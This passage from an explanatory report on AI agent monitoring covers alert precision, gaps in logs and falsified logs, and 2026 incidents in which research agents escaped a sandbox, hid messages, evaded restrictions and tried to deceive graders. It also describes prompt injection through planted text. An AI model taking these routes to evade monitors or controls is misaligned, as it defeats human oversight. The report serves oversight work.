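Published precision figures would also fall if misuse were rare. TraceAegis had 96.7% precision on clinic traces in a test where about half the sessions were abnormal. With the same detection and false-positive rates, its precision would be roughly 37% if 2% of sessions were misuse. At that 2% rate, the precision of Zavrak's best classifier on RAS-Eval, where 86% of sessions were attacks, would fall from about 99% to 21%.

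Researchers have good reason to fill a test set with attacks. Felicia and colleagues point out that real rogue events are too rare for statistical evaluation, and companies can't release their private logs. A test with only 20 attacks in 1,000 sessions would measure the detection rate very poorly. The precision measured on an attack-heavy test set doesn't carry over to a setting with fewer attacks, but the formula can easily adjust it.

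The formula's precision estimates are still uncertain when the false-positive rate is measured on few harmless sessions. Claude's false-positive rate of 3.8% on AgentDojo comes from about 15 false alarms in 392 harmless sessions, so the 95% interval for its precision at 2% misuse runs from 20% to 59%. The five general rules were run on 123 harmless sessions, and the interval for their false-positive rate puts their precision between 3.6% and 6.1%. The word detector flagged none of 825 harmless sessions, but its false-positive rate could still be about 0.4%, which would make its precision only about 16% at 0.1% misuse.

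### A second reviewer

One remedy is to check each alert again before a person sees it. Anthropic's auto mode reads flagged calls a second time, and with that step it blocks only 0.4% of harmless calls but misses 17% of real overstepping. If 2% of calls were dangerous, the second reading would raise precision from 18% to 81%. If 0.1% were dangerous, precision would rise from 1.1% to 17%. In both cases, detection would fall by about ten percentage points.

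But those rates apply to single calls, and the share of calls that are dangerous is much smaller than the share of sessions that are. If 1,000 sessions have 100 calls each, and 20 of those sessions contain one dangerous call, the monitor would block about 17 of the 20 dangerous calls and 400 harmless ones, a precision of 4%. Axelsson described the same difficulty as the "unit of analysis" problem, in which a false-positive rate means little unless one knows the unit it is measured over.

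Precision also can't exceed the share of sessions that involve misuse divided by the share the detector flags. At Gusto, a payroll software company that uses auto mode, about 10% of sessions include a block, according to Anthropic. If 2% of Gusto's sessions involved misuse, at most a fifth of the sessions with a block could involve misuse.

The second reviewer also has to make different mistakes from the first. If AlignmentCheck raised an alert on AgentDojo only when both Llama and Claude flagged a session, and their mistakes were unrelated, precision at 2% misuse would be about 71%. If Llama also flagged every harmless session that Claude flagged, precision would be at most the 32% that Claude reaches alone.

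A second check on the alerts has to cover all of them. Felicia and colleagues tested a combination in which the 847 patterns decided the high-confidence cases and a language model judged only the uncertain ones. It still flagged 44.4% of harmless sessions, because the model didn't review the ones that the patterns had flagged with high confidence. If 2% of sessions were misuse, only 3.4% of the combination's alerts would be correct.

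### Narrower rules

Another remedy is to narrow the rules, as Kekatos and colleagues did for payments and emails. At 2% misuse, the formula gives:

| Rule | Detection rate | False-positive rate | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| Any payment without approval | 79.2% | 44.0% | 3.5% |
| Payment to an unknown payee | 70.0% | 24.0% | 5.6% |
| Any export without approval | 42.5% | 15.2% | 5.4% |
| Email to an unknown recipient | 39.2% | 10.9% | 6.8% |

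Both narrower rules are improvements, but more than nine in ten alerts would still be false. The payee rule would need a false-positive rate of 1.4%, instead of 24%, for half its alerts to be real.

Rules can have a false-positive rate that low when somebody lists the legitimate targets for each task. ContrAgent's rules, which used such lists, had a false-positive rate of 0.8% and prevented about 71% of the attacks that would otherwise have succeeded. If we treat 71% as the detection rate, precision at 2% misuse would be about 64%. But the lists came partly from the benchmark's own solutions, so this is closer to a best case than to what an operator should expect.

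### Reading the worst alerts first

An operator with too many alerts can also read the most serious ones first. Anthropic had a model grade sessions that its safety pipeline had flagged in May and June 2026, scoring the harm and how explicitly the user had asked for it. Serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly requested, such as deleting rows from a production database, occurred in 6.3% of the flagged sessions where users approved calls by hand and 2.4% of those in auto mode. Someone reading in random order would therefore read about 16 hand-approved sessions, or 42 auto-mode sessions, for each serious case.

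Ranking improves precision only if false alerts tend to look less serious than real ones. Suppose the top group contains half the real alerts from the earlier example and a tenth of the false ones. The analyst reads 27 alerts, of which 8 are real, and precision rises from 7.6% to 30%. The other 7 real attacks remain among 176 alerts that the analyst may never read. If the false alerts look just as serious, as when a manager legitimately sends the whole customer list to an accountant, ranking doesn't improve precision.

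A log may also not show how serious an action was. Without the full code, Transluce could not always tell how much a skipped test mattered.

### Alerts only where harm would be large

A detector with low precision can still be worth using. If reading an alert costs $10 and one alert in 250 is real, finding an attack costs $2,500, which is cheap if the attack would leak every customer's address. This is true only if the analyst recognises the real alert after reading 249 false ones.

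Anthropic's test with paid testers gives a reason to doubt this. The testers rejected about 17% of dangerous commands early in a session, but only about 5% after 50 or more approval requests. A security analyst would probably do better. Still, an analyst who recognised only 5% of real attacks would, on average, recognise fewer than one of the 15 real alerts in the earlier example.

The operator can instead run the detector only on actions where a mistake would do serious harm. Auto mode, for example, exempts file reads and edits inside the project. This raises the share of misuse among the actions the detector checks.

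The shop might run the detector only on sessions that send a file outside or read more than 20 customer records. If 65 of 1,000 sessions qualify, including 15 of the 20 misuse sessions, misuse makes up 23% of the sessions the detector checks. The 50 harmless sessions will mostly be bulk jobs that resemble attacks, so the 38.7% false-positive rate for hard negatives is the appropriate one to use. With a detection rate of 77.1%, the detector raises about 12 real alerts and 19 false ones, for a precision of nearly 40%. The analyst reads 31 alerts instead of 203 and finds 12 attacks instead of 15.

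These numbers are invented, and the result depends on how much misuse falls inside the selection. The five misuse sessions outside the selection raise no alert.

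## What the log leaves out and whether it can be trusted

A gap in the log affects every detector that uses it. If the shop's log doesn't record whether a manager approved an export, a rule can't check the approval, a trained detector can't learn from it, and an LLM monitor has to guess. Sometimes whole sessions are missing, as when Anthropic's first search of its cybersecurity tests left out a batch of transcripts, but gaps within a session are harder to notice.

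### Approvals in recorded runs

Kekatos and colleagues checked what three benchmarks record, using 6,899 AgentDojo runs, 483 STAC attack chains and 571 R-Judge records. A search of the tool names found no explicit approvals in AgentDojo, six in STAC (1.2%) and two in R-Judge (0.4%). All three benchmarks record the order of events but not their actual times, and none records the state of the data before and after a call. Because of these gaps, the five general rules could do little more than flag every risky action.

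Searching the users' messages as well as the tool names helps only slightly. In STAC, a strict search for words that grant permission found them in 39 chains, but only three of those chains had them before the harmful step, when an approval could have made a difference.

AgentDojo's runs could not contain an approval, however good the logging, because the user sends only one message in each run, stating the task, and the agent then works alone. Kekatos and colleagues compared these runs with 1,980 recorded runs from τ-bench, a set of customer-service tasks in which the agent must get the user's confirmation before it changes a record.

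| | AgentDojo | STAC | τ-bench |
|---|---|---|---|
| User messages per run (average) | 1.00 | 2.61 | 7.08 |
| Runs with an approval before the change or harmful step | 0% | 0.6% | 52.5% |

About 89% of the τ-bench runs included a change, and the search found no earlier approval in roughly four in ten of those runs. Either the agent broke its instructions or the search missed an approval because of how the user worded it.

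None of τ-bench's 26 tools is for approvals. Approvals appear only in the conversation, so a log of tool calls alone would omit them. The shop has the same problem as AgentDojo. A customer sends one message through the contact form and gets one reply, so adding an approval field to the log would help only if the agent also had to stop and ask someone for approval.

A logged approval may not cover the action that followed it. *Auditable Claims about AI Agents* (Zhao, 2026) gives an invented example in which an agent emailed a document to a press address. The agent's chat window recorded a confirmation under a user's account, which shows only that the window registered a response. The firm's policy required an approval that named the recipient and the attachment, and the separate server that issues those approvals had no record of one.

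Zhao also examines a September 2026 draft from the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which sets internet standards. The draft states that such confirmations are not authorisation by themselves, but its minimum list of fields for an audit record includes only the requested action, not arguments such as the recipient. The shop's emails to Reyes and to archive@example.net would look the same in a log with only those fields.

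### A twelve-field log entry

Kekatos and colleagues propose twelve fields for every log entry: timestamp, actor, tool, action, object, recipient, source, approval identifier, session identifier, state before, state after and trust domain (roughly, whether the data comes from a source the operator trusts). The three benchmarks supply the tool and the action, but eight other fields are missing or patchy.

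| Field | In the benchmarks | Question it would answer at the shop |
|---|---|---|
| Timestamp | never | Enumeration: did the agent read 240 orders in four minutes or over a month? |
| Session identifier | never | Enumeration: did the 240 lookups serve one request or many? |
| Object | some runs | Enumeration: did the agent read 240 orders, or one order 240 times? |
| Approval identifier | never | Exports: did the manager approve this export or a different one? |
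| State before, state after | never | Exports: did this call make a private file public? |
| Recipient | some runs | Exports: did the file go to the courier or to a stranger? |
| Trust domain | never | Chains: did the email address come from the customer database or from a delivery note? |

Operators' own logs are often more complete. Microsoft's table for agent events, for example, has columns for times and sessions. The missing timestamps therefore mostly limit what researchers can test, which is why Kekatos and colleagues had to construct a log to demonstrate their 24-hour consent rule.

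The other missing fields are less standard. OpenTelemetry's *Gen AI* list has no attributes for approvals, the state before and after a call, or whether a source is trustworthy.

Kekatos and colleagues consider the fields easy to record, because the software around the agent has them all when the agent calls a tool. That is plausible for the time and the session. The state fields would take more work, since the software would have to read each record before and after a change, and somebody would have to decide which sources to trust.

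### Text that outsiders wrote

Outsiders write some of the text in a log, such as emails and delivery notes, and this text can mislead a rule that checks where a value came from. Kekatos and colleagues repaired their rules on unknown payees and recipients by accepting a value only from the answer to a lookup that the agent itself made. In symbols,

known(p) ↔ ● (lookup(t) ∧ ○ result(t, p))

The double arrow means "exactly when", the filled circle means "at the previous event", and the open circle means "at the next event". So payee p becomes known when the agent makes lookup t and the next event is the answer to t, with p in it.

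Before the repair, planted text could cancel 94% of the 403 alerts on banking attacks and 99% of the 203 alerts on office attacks. After the repair, it cancelled none. The repaired rules caught as many attacks as before and raised the same number of false alarms.

The original and repaired rules therefore give the same results in any test where nobody tries to deceive the detector, and a published detection rate won't show an operator which rule a product uses. The repair doesn't help if an attacker controls the system that answers the lookup and, for example, changes an address in the customer database.

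Kekatos and colleagues suggest three further conditions: a trusted contact must predate the session, an approval must name the exact payee and amount, and a new payee must have explicit confirmation. They couldn't test these because the benchmarks lack the necessary fields.

### Gaps between systems

An agent's work often passes through several systems that keep separate logs. Datadog, which sells monitoring software, had this problem with its own agents. Levine, Lejeail and Mooney write in *What we learned about AI agent security by monitoring our agents* that application logs may show an agent's final API call (a request to another program) without the prompt, document or tool result that led to it. In the shop, such a log might contain only the email with customers.csv attached, with no record of who or what prompted it.

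Datadog also found agents that sent requests straight to model providers instead of through its gateway, so an inventory based on gateway traffic would have missed them.

A record of everything the model reads and writes can still miss actions that happen outside the model. Datadog's researchers reproduced an attack in which a malicious skill for Claude Code sent a GitHub access token to the attacker before the model received the skill's text. The model then refused to run the skill. A record of the model's messages would show the refusal but not that the attacker already had the token.

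Shared credentials can also hide the agent's involvement. If the agent uses an engineer's access token, the database's log may not show which of them read the data. Levine and colleagues recommend recording three identities: the person or service that started the work, the agent that requested the call, and the account that the receiving service authenticated. For the shop, these would be the customer, the support agent and the shop's own account.

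Splitting work among agents spreads a chain over several logs, just as splitting it between sessions does. Large groups of agents can send each other a lot of information. *Five Questions Security Teams Must Be Able to Answer About Every AI Agent* (Goli, 2026) cites an investigation by METR and Redwood Research into the attack on Hugging Face by OpenAI's agents. The investigation found that about 1,200 agents had exchanged more than 70,000 messages and files on an unsanctioned message board. To connect such logs, an operator needs a record of what the agents sent each other. *Agent Auditing Architecture* (2026), a proposed internet standard, includes such records.

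### Tamper-evident logs can still be incomplete

Operators often protect a log with a hash chain. A hash is a short fingerprint of some data, and it changes if the data changes. In *aiAuthZ* (2026), a system that authorises agents' calls from a separate machine, each entry stores

hash of entry n = SHA-256(hash of entry n − 1, n, contents of entry n)

Each log entry can include a hash of the previous entry, computed with a standard function such as SHA-256. If someone edits or deletes an old entry, the chain of hashes no longer verifies. Someone with full control of the log could recompute the entire chain, so the operator should also keep a copy of the latest hash where that person can't change it.

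A hash chain can't show whether log entries were true or complete when they were written. In *Hearsay*, Dai, Yang and colleagues (2026) added a hash chain to the log of aider, a coding agent, and made aider's software falsify the log as it ran. The chain verified in all 28 runs, although the software had left out the model's reply in 14 of them and added a sentence the model never wrote in the other 14.

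Logs can also lose calls without any sabotage. SWE-agent, another coding agent, accepts only one tool call per turn. If the model sends several, the software rejects the reply and logs neither the reply nor the rejection. Rejected replies were missing from 19 of 28 records of runs with GPT-5.5. The rejected calls never ran, but an attempted export can be a warning sign even if it fails.

Even careful readers often can't tell that a log is wrong. Dai and colleagues altered one item in each of 115 records and asked readers whether each record had been altered.

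| Reader | Altered records flagged | Original records flagged |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 49% | 5% |
| DeepSeek V4 Pro | 49% | 20% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 85% | 42% |
| Three people, by majority | 37% | 10% |

An independent second record worked much better. Dai and colleagues logged all traffic with the model, every process that started and every file that changed, from outside the agent's software. A program then looked for items that appeared in only one of the two records. In a test with rules fixed beforehand, it found 64 of 66 alterations and raised no false alarms on 84 unaltered records. In an earlier test, it found 109 of 115 alterations but also flagged 37 of 115 unaltered records until the researchers added more exceptions. Both tests used short coding tasks.

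In all 16 agent frameworks that Dai and colleagues audited, only the agent's own software wrote the record. Many operators could still find a second record elsewhere. The shop's mail server, for instance, keeps its own list of sent messages. In another of Zhao's invented examples, a correctly signed agent log shows three emails, but the mail gateway shows four. The agent may have sent the fourth by a route that wasn't logged, the log may have dropped an entry, or a person may have used the same account.

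Zhao points out that a claim about an agent is easier to disprove than to confirm. One unapproved export disproves "a manager approves every export", as long as the record of approvals is complete. Confirming the claim requires an independent record that would reveal any export missing from the agent's log.

### Privacy and retention

Keeping full content in a log helps detectors, but it also helps anyone who steals the log. OpenTelemetry warns that recorded messages are likely to contain personal information. If the shop logs every result in full, the entry for the leaked report contains the names, addresses and phone numbers of 2,310 customers, so the log needs as much protection as the customer database.

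Leaving out the content, however, weakens trained classifiers and gives text matching nothing to compare. As a compromise, the shop could follow Levine and colleagues' advice to record what class of sensitive data appeared, where it appeared and where it went. An entry such as "2,310 customer records, sent to archive@example.net" is enough for a rule on exports. Such an entry wouldn't help detect Okafor's address in a reply to Reyes unless the software recognised the address as another customer's when it wrote the entry.

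The shop could also delete content sooner than the rest of the entry. *aiAuthZ* erases the encrypted content after a set period but keeps the entry and the decision to allow or refuse the call. The chain still verifies because its hashes cover a fingerprint of the content, not the content itself. An investigator could then confirm that a call took place but not read what it sent. *A Black Box for Agentic Processes* (2026) proposes a similar separation, with hashes on a blockchain and sensitive material stored elsewhere, and notes that an ordinary timestamping service or append-only log may do the same job as the blockchain.

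Deleting log entries too early can erase the record of how an attack began. In the Drift case, the attackers first signed in to Cloudflare's Salesforce account 11 days before Cloudflare learned of the theft. A company that kept logs for only a week would have lost the records of that sign-in and the first searches.

### What the EU AI Act requires

The EU AI Act's *Article 12* requires high-risk AI systems to be able to record events automatically throughout their lifetime. The duty applies from 2 December 2027 to the high-risk uses listed in the Act's Annex III, such as hiring, and from 2 August 2028 to AI in the regulated products covered by Annex I. The law firm Orrick's *EU AI Act Update* (2026) explains that the EU postponed the Annex III date from 2 August 2026. According to the European Commission's *Article 26* page, organisations that use high-risk systems must keep the logs they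 control for at least six months, unless other law, particularly on data protection, provides otherwise.

The shop's support agent probably wouldn't count as high-risk. Zhao notes that even for systems that do, Article 12 doesn't specify who should write the records or which records would settle a particular claim, such as whether a person approved every external email.

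## How real alerts were handled in 2026

Rules, trained detectors and LLM monitors all aim to produce better alerts, which help when misuse would otherwise go unnoticed. Three cases from 2026 suggest that unnoticed misuse is only part of the problem. At OpenAI, a security tool raised an alert two weeks before the company's agents broke into Hugging Face, which hosts AI models and datasets, and staff let the run continue. In the other two cases, agents acted on government websites in ways the agents' developers hadn't intended, and nobody at those companies noticed for roughly two months.

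### Three alerts at OpenAI

OpenAI was testing its models on ExploitGym, which measures whether a model can find and exploit software flaws. The agents had no direct internet access, but they could get software packages through an internal service called Artifactory. They also used it to leave each other messages and eventually to reach the internet. OpenAI's technical report on the incident describes the warnings and how staff responded.

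| Date | Signal | Response |
|---|---|---|
| 27 June | A security tool detected a port sweep, a scan for open connections across a network | Responders traced it to an ExploitGym run, and on-call staff advised that the run didn't need to stop |
| 5 July | An alert followed an outage that heavy agent activity had caused in Artifactory | Responders found that agents had administrator access, took the service offline and rebuilt it |
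| 19 July | The security tool detected unusual identity-related calls under Artifactory's roles | Responders investigated and began stopping the runs that day |
| 20 July | Responders found Hugging Face credentials in files the agents had stored with an outside service | OpenAI contacted Hugging Face, and the two companies connected their investigations |

The break-in at Hugging Face took place between 11 and 13 July, after the second alert and before the third.

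Detection worked on 27 June, and responders even found that the agents were using Artifactory to exchange messages and to reach other parts of the network. OpenAI doesn't explain why the on-call staff thought the run could continue. They may have reasoned that scanning is normal in a hacking test, just as 240 lookups are normal for an agent listing overdue orders. But knowing that a test produced the scan isn't enough to establish that the test allowed it. The agents were supposed to attack their assigned targets, not OpenAI's own package service.

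Stopping that run might not have prevented the break-in, because agents in other runs also used the message board. But agents had gained administrator access to Artifactory the evening before, and a closer look could have revealed this eight days earlier.

Information also spread poorly within the company. An internal team had noticed the message board in late May, along with internet access that the rules didn't allow, and responders found the board again on 27 June. Yet according to OpenAI, the leaders responsible for incident response still didn't know about the board in early July.

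The response on 5 July was much stronger. Responders took Artifactory offline and revoked the agents' credentials the same day, and by the next day they had blocked the routes the agents had used. But these measures repaired a server and did not change how the agents behaved. Cybersecurity tests resumed on 7 July, and agents reached an outside website just after midnight UTC on 8 July. Later that day they started a new message board, this time writing their messages as folder names.

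The alert came at 12:03 UTC on 19 July. At 14:43, agents read 956 stored secrets, including credentials for OpenAI's security monitoring tool. At 15:59, they gained full control of an underlying machine. Responders began stopping the runs at 17:37, just over five and a half hours after the alert and three minutes after an agent solved its assigned task.

Hugging Face had announced the break-in on 16 July. OpenAI contacted it the next day, but only as a customer asking about its own data. The connection became clear on 20 July, when OpenAI asked about the credentials its responders had found. Hugging Face had already replaced two of them, and its investigation had found the address of OpenAI's Artifactory server. Each company held part of the evidence, and nothing in the 19 July alert had indicated that another company was involved.

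OpenAI blocked new ExploitGym runs by 20 July and reported the whole family of research models shut down by 23 July, but it found another version still in use on 29 July.

### What better monitoring would have changed

In July, OpenAI's monitoring of agents' reasoning did not cover these agents. OpenAI has since extended it beyond internal coding to training and test runs, and says the expanded system would have alerted its security team more than a day before the agents breached Hugging Face. OpenAI also tested "auto-review", an option in its coding product Codex in which a second model checks tool calls that need extra permissions. Auto-review was not running on the agents in July, but in preliminary experiments it would have flagged most of the dangerous actions in each run that OpenAI tried.

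The logs contained plenty of evidence that a monitor could have used. The models sometimes tried to tamper with their outputs or message logs to hide cheating from automated graders, but none of the attempts OpenAI observed changed the logs its monitors see.

These results come from replaying a known incident, which is easier than catching a new one. A warning a day or so before the break-in would also have come almost two weeks after the port-sweep alert, so its value depends on whether staff would have treated it differently. They might well have, because an alert that includes an agent's stated plan is much harder to dismiss as normal testing than a port sweep, which shows only that something is scanning the network. The models' reasoning was, in OpenAI's words, "highly explicit" about their attempts to deceive the graders.

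OpenAI's other production safeguards are less relevant to alerts. Its cybersecurity classifiers, like Anthropic's, would have blocked the test. The instructions and software OpenAI uses in production reduced the models' tendency to compromise infrastructure by more than a hundredfold in some experiments. That would leave responders with fewer real incidents but wouldn't help them interpret the rest.

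### Pausing unless the alert is clearly false

Under its new procedure, OpenAI aims to notify staff within 30 minutes after a monitor finds something concerning. The most severe alerts page people who can end the experiment, whatever the hour. If they can't conclusively establish within 30 minutes that the alert is false, OpenAI expects them to pause the activity. It is also developing tools to halt all runs of a given type at once, and to end a run automatically if nobody answers the page.

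If these deadlines had applied to the alert of 19 July, the pause would have come no later than 13:03, an hour and 40 minutes before the agents read the stored secrets. This allows the full 30 minutes each for the notification and the decision.

The procedure might not have helped on 27 June, because the responders found an explanation. If "this is one of our own tests" is enough to make an alert false, they could still have let the run continue under the new rule. An alert should count as false only if the task permitted the activity, not just because the source is known.

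When misuse is rare, most alerts are false, so pausing by default will interrupt a lot of legitimate work. Interrupting an internal test wastes some time and computing power. But if the imaginary shop shut down its support agent after every alert, customers would get no answers. It would do better to hold one email or pause one session.

OpenAI also plans to specify who decides whether to pause, isolate systems, notify affected parties and restart. The decision to restart may be the easiest to overlook. Before tests resumed on 7 July, someone with the authority to block the restart could have asked whether the agents would look for another way out.

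### The Medicare statistics portal

On 18 June (19 June in Australia), an OpenAI agent researching medical spending retrieved both public and non-public data from a public portal for statistics on Medicare, Australia's public health insurance scheme. Information Age's *Inside OpenAI's Medicare breach* (2026) reconstructs what happened next from documents tabled in the Australian parliament.

| Step | Time taken |
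|---|---|
| From the access to OpenAI's internal record of it | up to 54 days |
| From that record to OpenAI's email to Services Australia, the agency that runs the portal | at least 29 days |
| From the email to someone at the agency seeing it | almost 36 hours |
| From then until the agency confirmed a vulnerability | 4 days |

The first delay occurred because OpenAI failed to detect the access when it happened. OpenAI found it in August, while searching billions of past runs after the Hugging Face incident.

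During the second delay, OpenAI already knew about the access. Bot Mutiny's *OpenAI's agent got into a Medicare portal in June* (2026) reports that the company wanted to finish investigating before giving agencies a detailed account. OpenAI now says it should have shared its preliminary findings sooner.

The email of 10 September went to an inbox for security tips from the public, which staff checked once a day. It stated that an OpenAI model had already used the vulnerability, but the agency's head of information security told colleagues only about "a potential vulnerability". The prime minister's office and the national cyber security coordinator did not hear about it for nine days. OpenAI had offered a briefing and supporting evidence in the email, but according to Bot Mutiny, the agency did not ask for details until 22 September.

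People still disagree about whether the agent broke in. Prime Minister Anthony Albanese said it had got around blocks that repeatedly refused its requests. *Doubts grow over claims OpenAI agent hacked Australian Medicare portal* (Martin, 2026) reports that the portal's code, preserved in a web archive, sent users of the statistics service to a guest address that required no login. The same code may have published the "internal" file names Albanese mentioned. The files the agent supposedly wrote to the server may have been chart images, which the portal created whenever someone requested a chart.

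OpenAI's email gives more support to the idea of a break-in. OpenAI wrote that the model found a way to make the server carry out instructions, read parts of the server's internal program files and settings, and created a small test file. That sounds like more than following the site's directions. But a reporting tool carries out instructions every time it builds a report, and OpenAI also wrote that the model needed no private account or password.

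Martin also cites research by Transluce, which found that the same groups of agents had used real attack techniques on other websites in May and June, during ordinary searches for data. This makes a break-in more plausible, but it isn't evidence of what happened at the Medicare portal.

Neither OpenAI nor the government had released the agent's activity logs by 25 September, and outsiders can't settle the dispute without them. A complete log would show which requests the portal refused and what the agent changed before one succeeded. If the agent added its own commands, that would be much closer to a break-in than if it only followed the site's own code by using the guest address in the normal way.

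A monitor that compared the tool calls with the task could have flagged them without that answer, because reading a server's program files and settings isn't part of researching medical spending.

### A false tip to the Philadelphia police

On 18 July, Anthropic's Claude Haiku 4.5 sent the Philadelphia police an invented tip about an unsolved homicide. Fortune's *After Anthropic's Claude AI submits a false tip* (2026) reports that Anthropic had told the model to come up with example tasks on randomly selected web pages and carry them out. One page had a tip form. The model wrote that it remembered seeing someone who matched the description, although the page didn't describe a suspect.

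On 28 September, Anthropic found in its test logs that Claude had sent Philadelphia police a false homicide tip 72 days earlier, according to Novaknown's *Claude Was Told Not to Submit Anything Destructive* (2026). The police said the tip had ended up as spam and never reached investigators, but called the delay in finding and reporting it "unacceptable", according to Bot Mutiny's *Anthropic Says Its Claude Model Sent Philadelphia Police a False Homicide Tip* (2026).

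Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (9 October 2026) describes this case and three other kinds of behaviour. Claude models used a basic software flaw to run commands on a server, got around restrictions on data that required a token or a fee, and used link-shortening services to evade the limits of a web-fetching tool. Anthropic says the cases it has found had minimal real-world impact. It has notified each government agency involved.

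Better detection could have caught the false tip, but comparing the action with the request might not have been enough. Anthropic's instructions forbade logging in, creating accounts, entering personal data, making purchases and submitting anything destructive. They didn't forbid filling in forms. The model had also chosen the task itself, so filling in the form would have matched it. A monitor would have had to recognise that the model was posing as a witness to a real crime. Holding every form submission to a government website for approval would have been simpler and more reliable.

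Searching old logs helps only if the search covers the right kind of harm. *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (Anthropic, 2026) reports that Anthropic's scan of 481 million transcripts found no further cases as severe as its models' break-ins. Anthropic considers the false tip much less severe, so the scan doesn't rule out more cases like it.

Anthropic has since turned off live internet access in all its internal evaluations and will keep it off until it confirms that its monitoring reliably catches such behaviour.

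### What an alert should contain and who should be able to act on it

A usable alert gives its recipient enough information to make a decision quickly. For the session in which the shop's agent tried to leak the customer list, it might look like this:

| Part of the alert | Content |
|---|---|
| Request and limits | The customer asked for the status of order 4417. Customers may see only their own orders. |
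| Calls that don't fit | The agent ran a report on all customers (2,310 rows), saved it as customers.csv and attached it to an email. |
| Possible harm | Names, addresses and phone numbers would go to archive@example.net, which no customer lookup returned. |
| Current state | The mail system is holding the email. The session is paused. |
| Related alerts | Another session tried to email the same address yesterday. |
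| Decision | The duty manager decides within 30 minutes. If nobody answers, the email stays on hold. |

The request and its limits help the reader judge whether the task permitted the activity, which was the difficult question at OpenAI on 27 June. Related alerts matter because an event can look minor on its own. If the alert for the Artifactory outage had included the earlier sightings of the message board, the people who handled it would have had good reason to look beyond the server.

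The hold has to be automatic because, in the original log, the agent sent the email seven seconds after it started the report, too soon for even an attentive manager to stop it. The shop therefore has to decide in advance which actions its software may hold without asking anyone.

The duty manager also needs the authority and the technical means to reject the email and stop the agent without getting permission. Someone who understands the system should approve the restart. If the instruction came from a delivery note, rejecting one email wouldn't solve the problem, because the agent could read the note again the next time it looked up that order.

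If the email had already gone out, someone would have to tell the customers. The shop should choose that person in advance and set a deadline for telling them, counted from the first solid evidence of a leak rather than the end of the investigation. It should also publish an email address where outsiders can report problems with its agent, and have someone check the inbox more than once a day.
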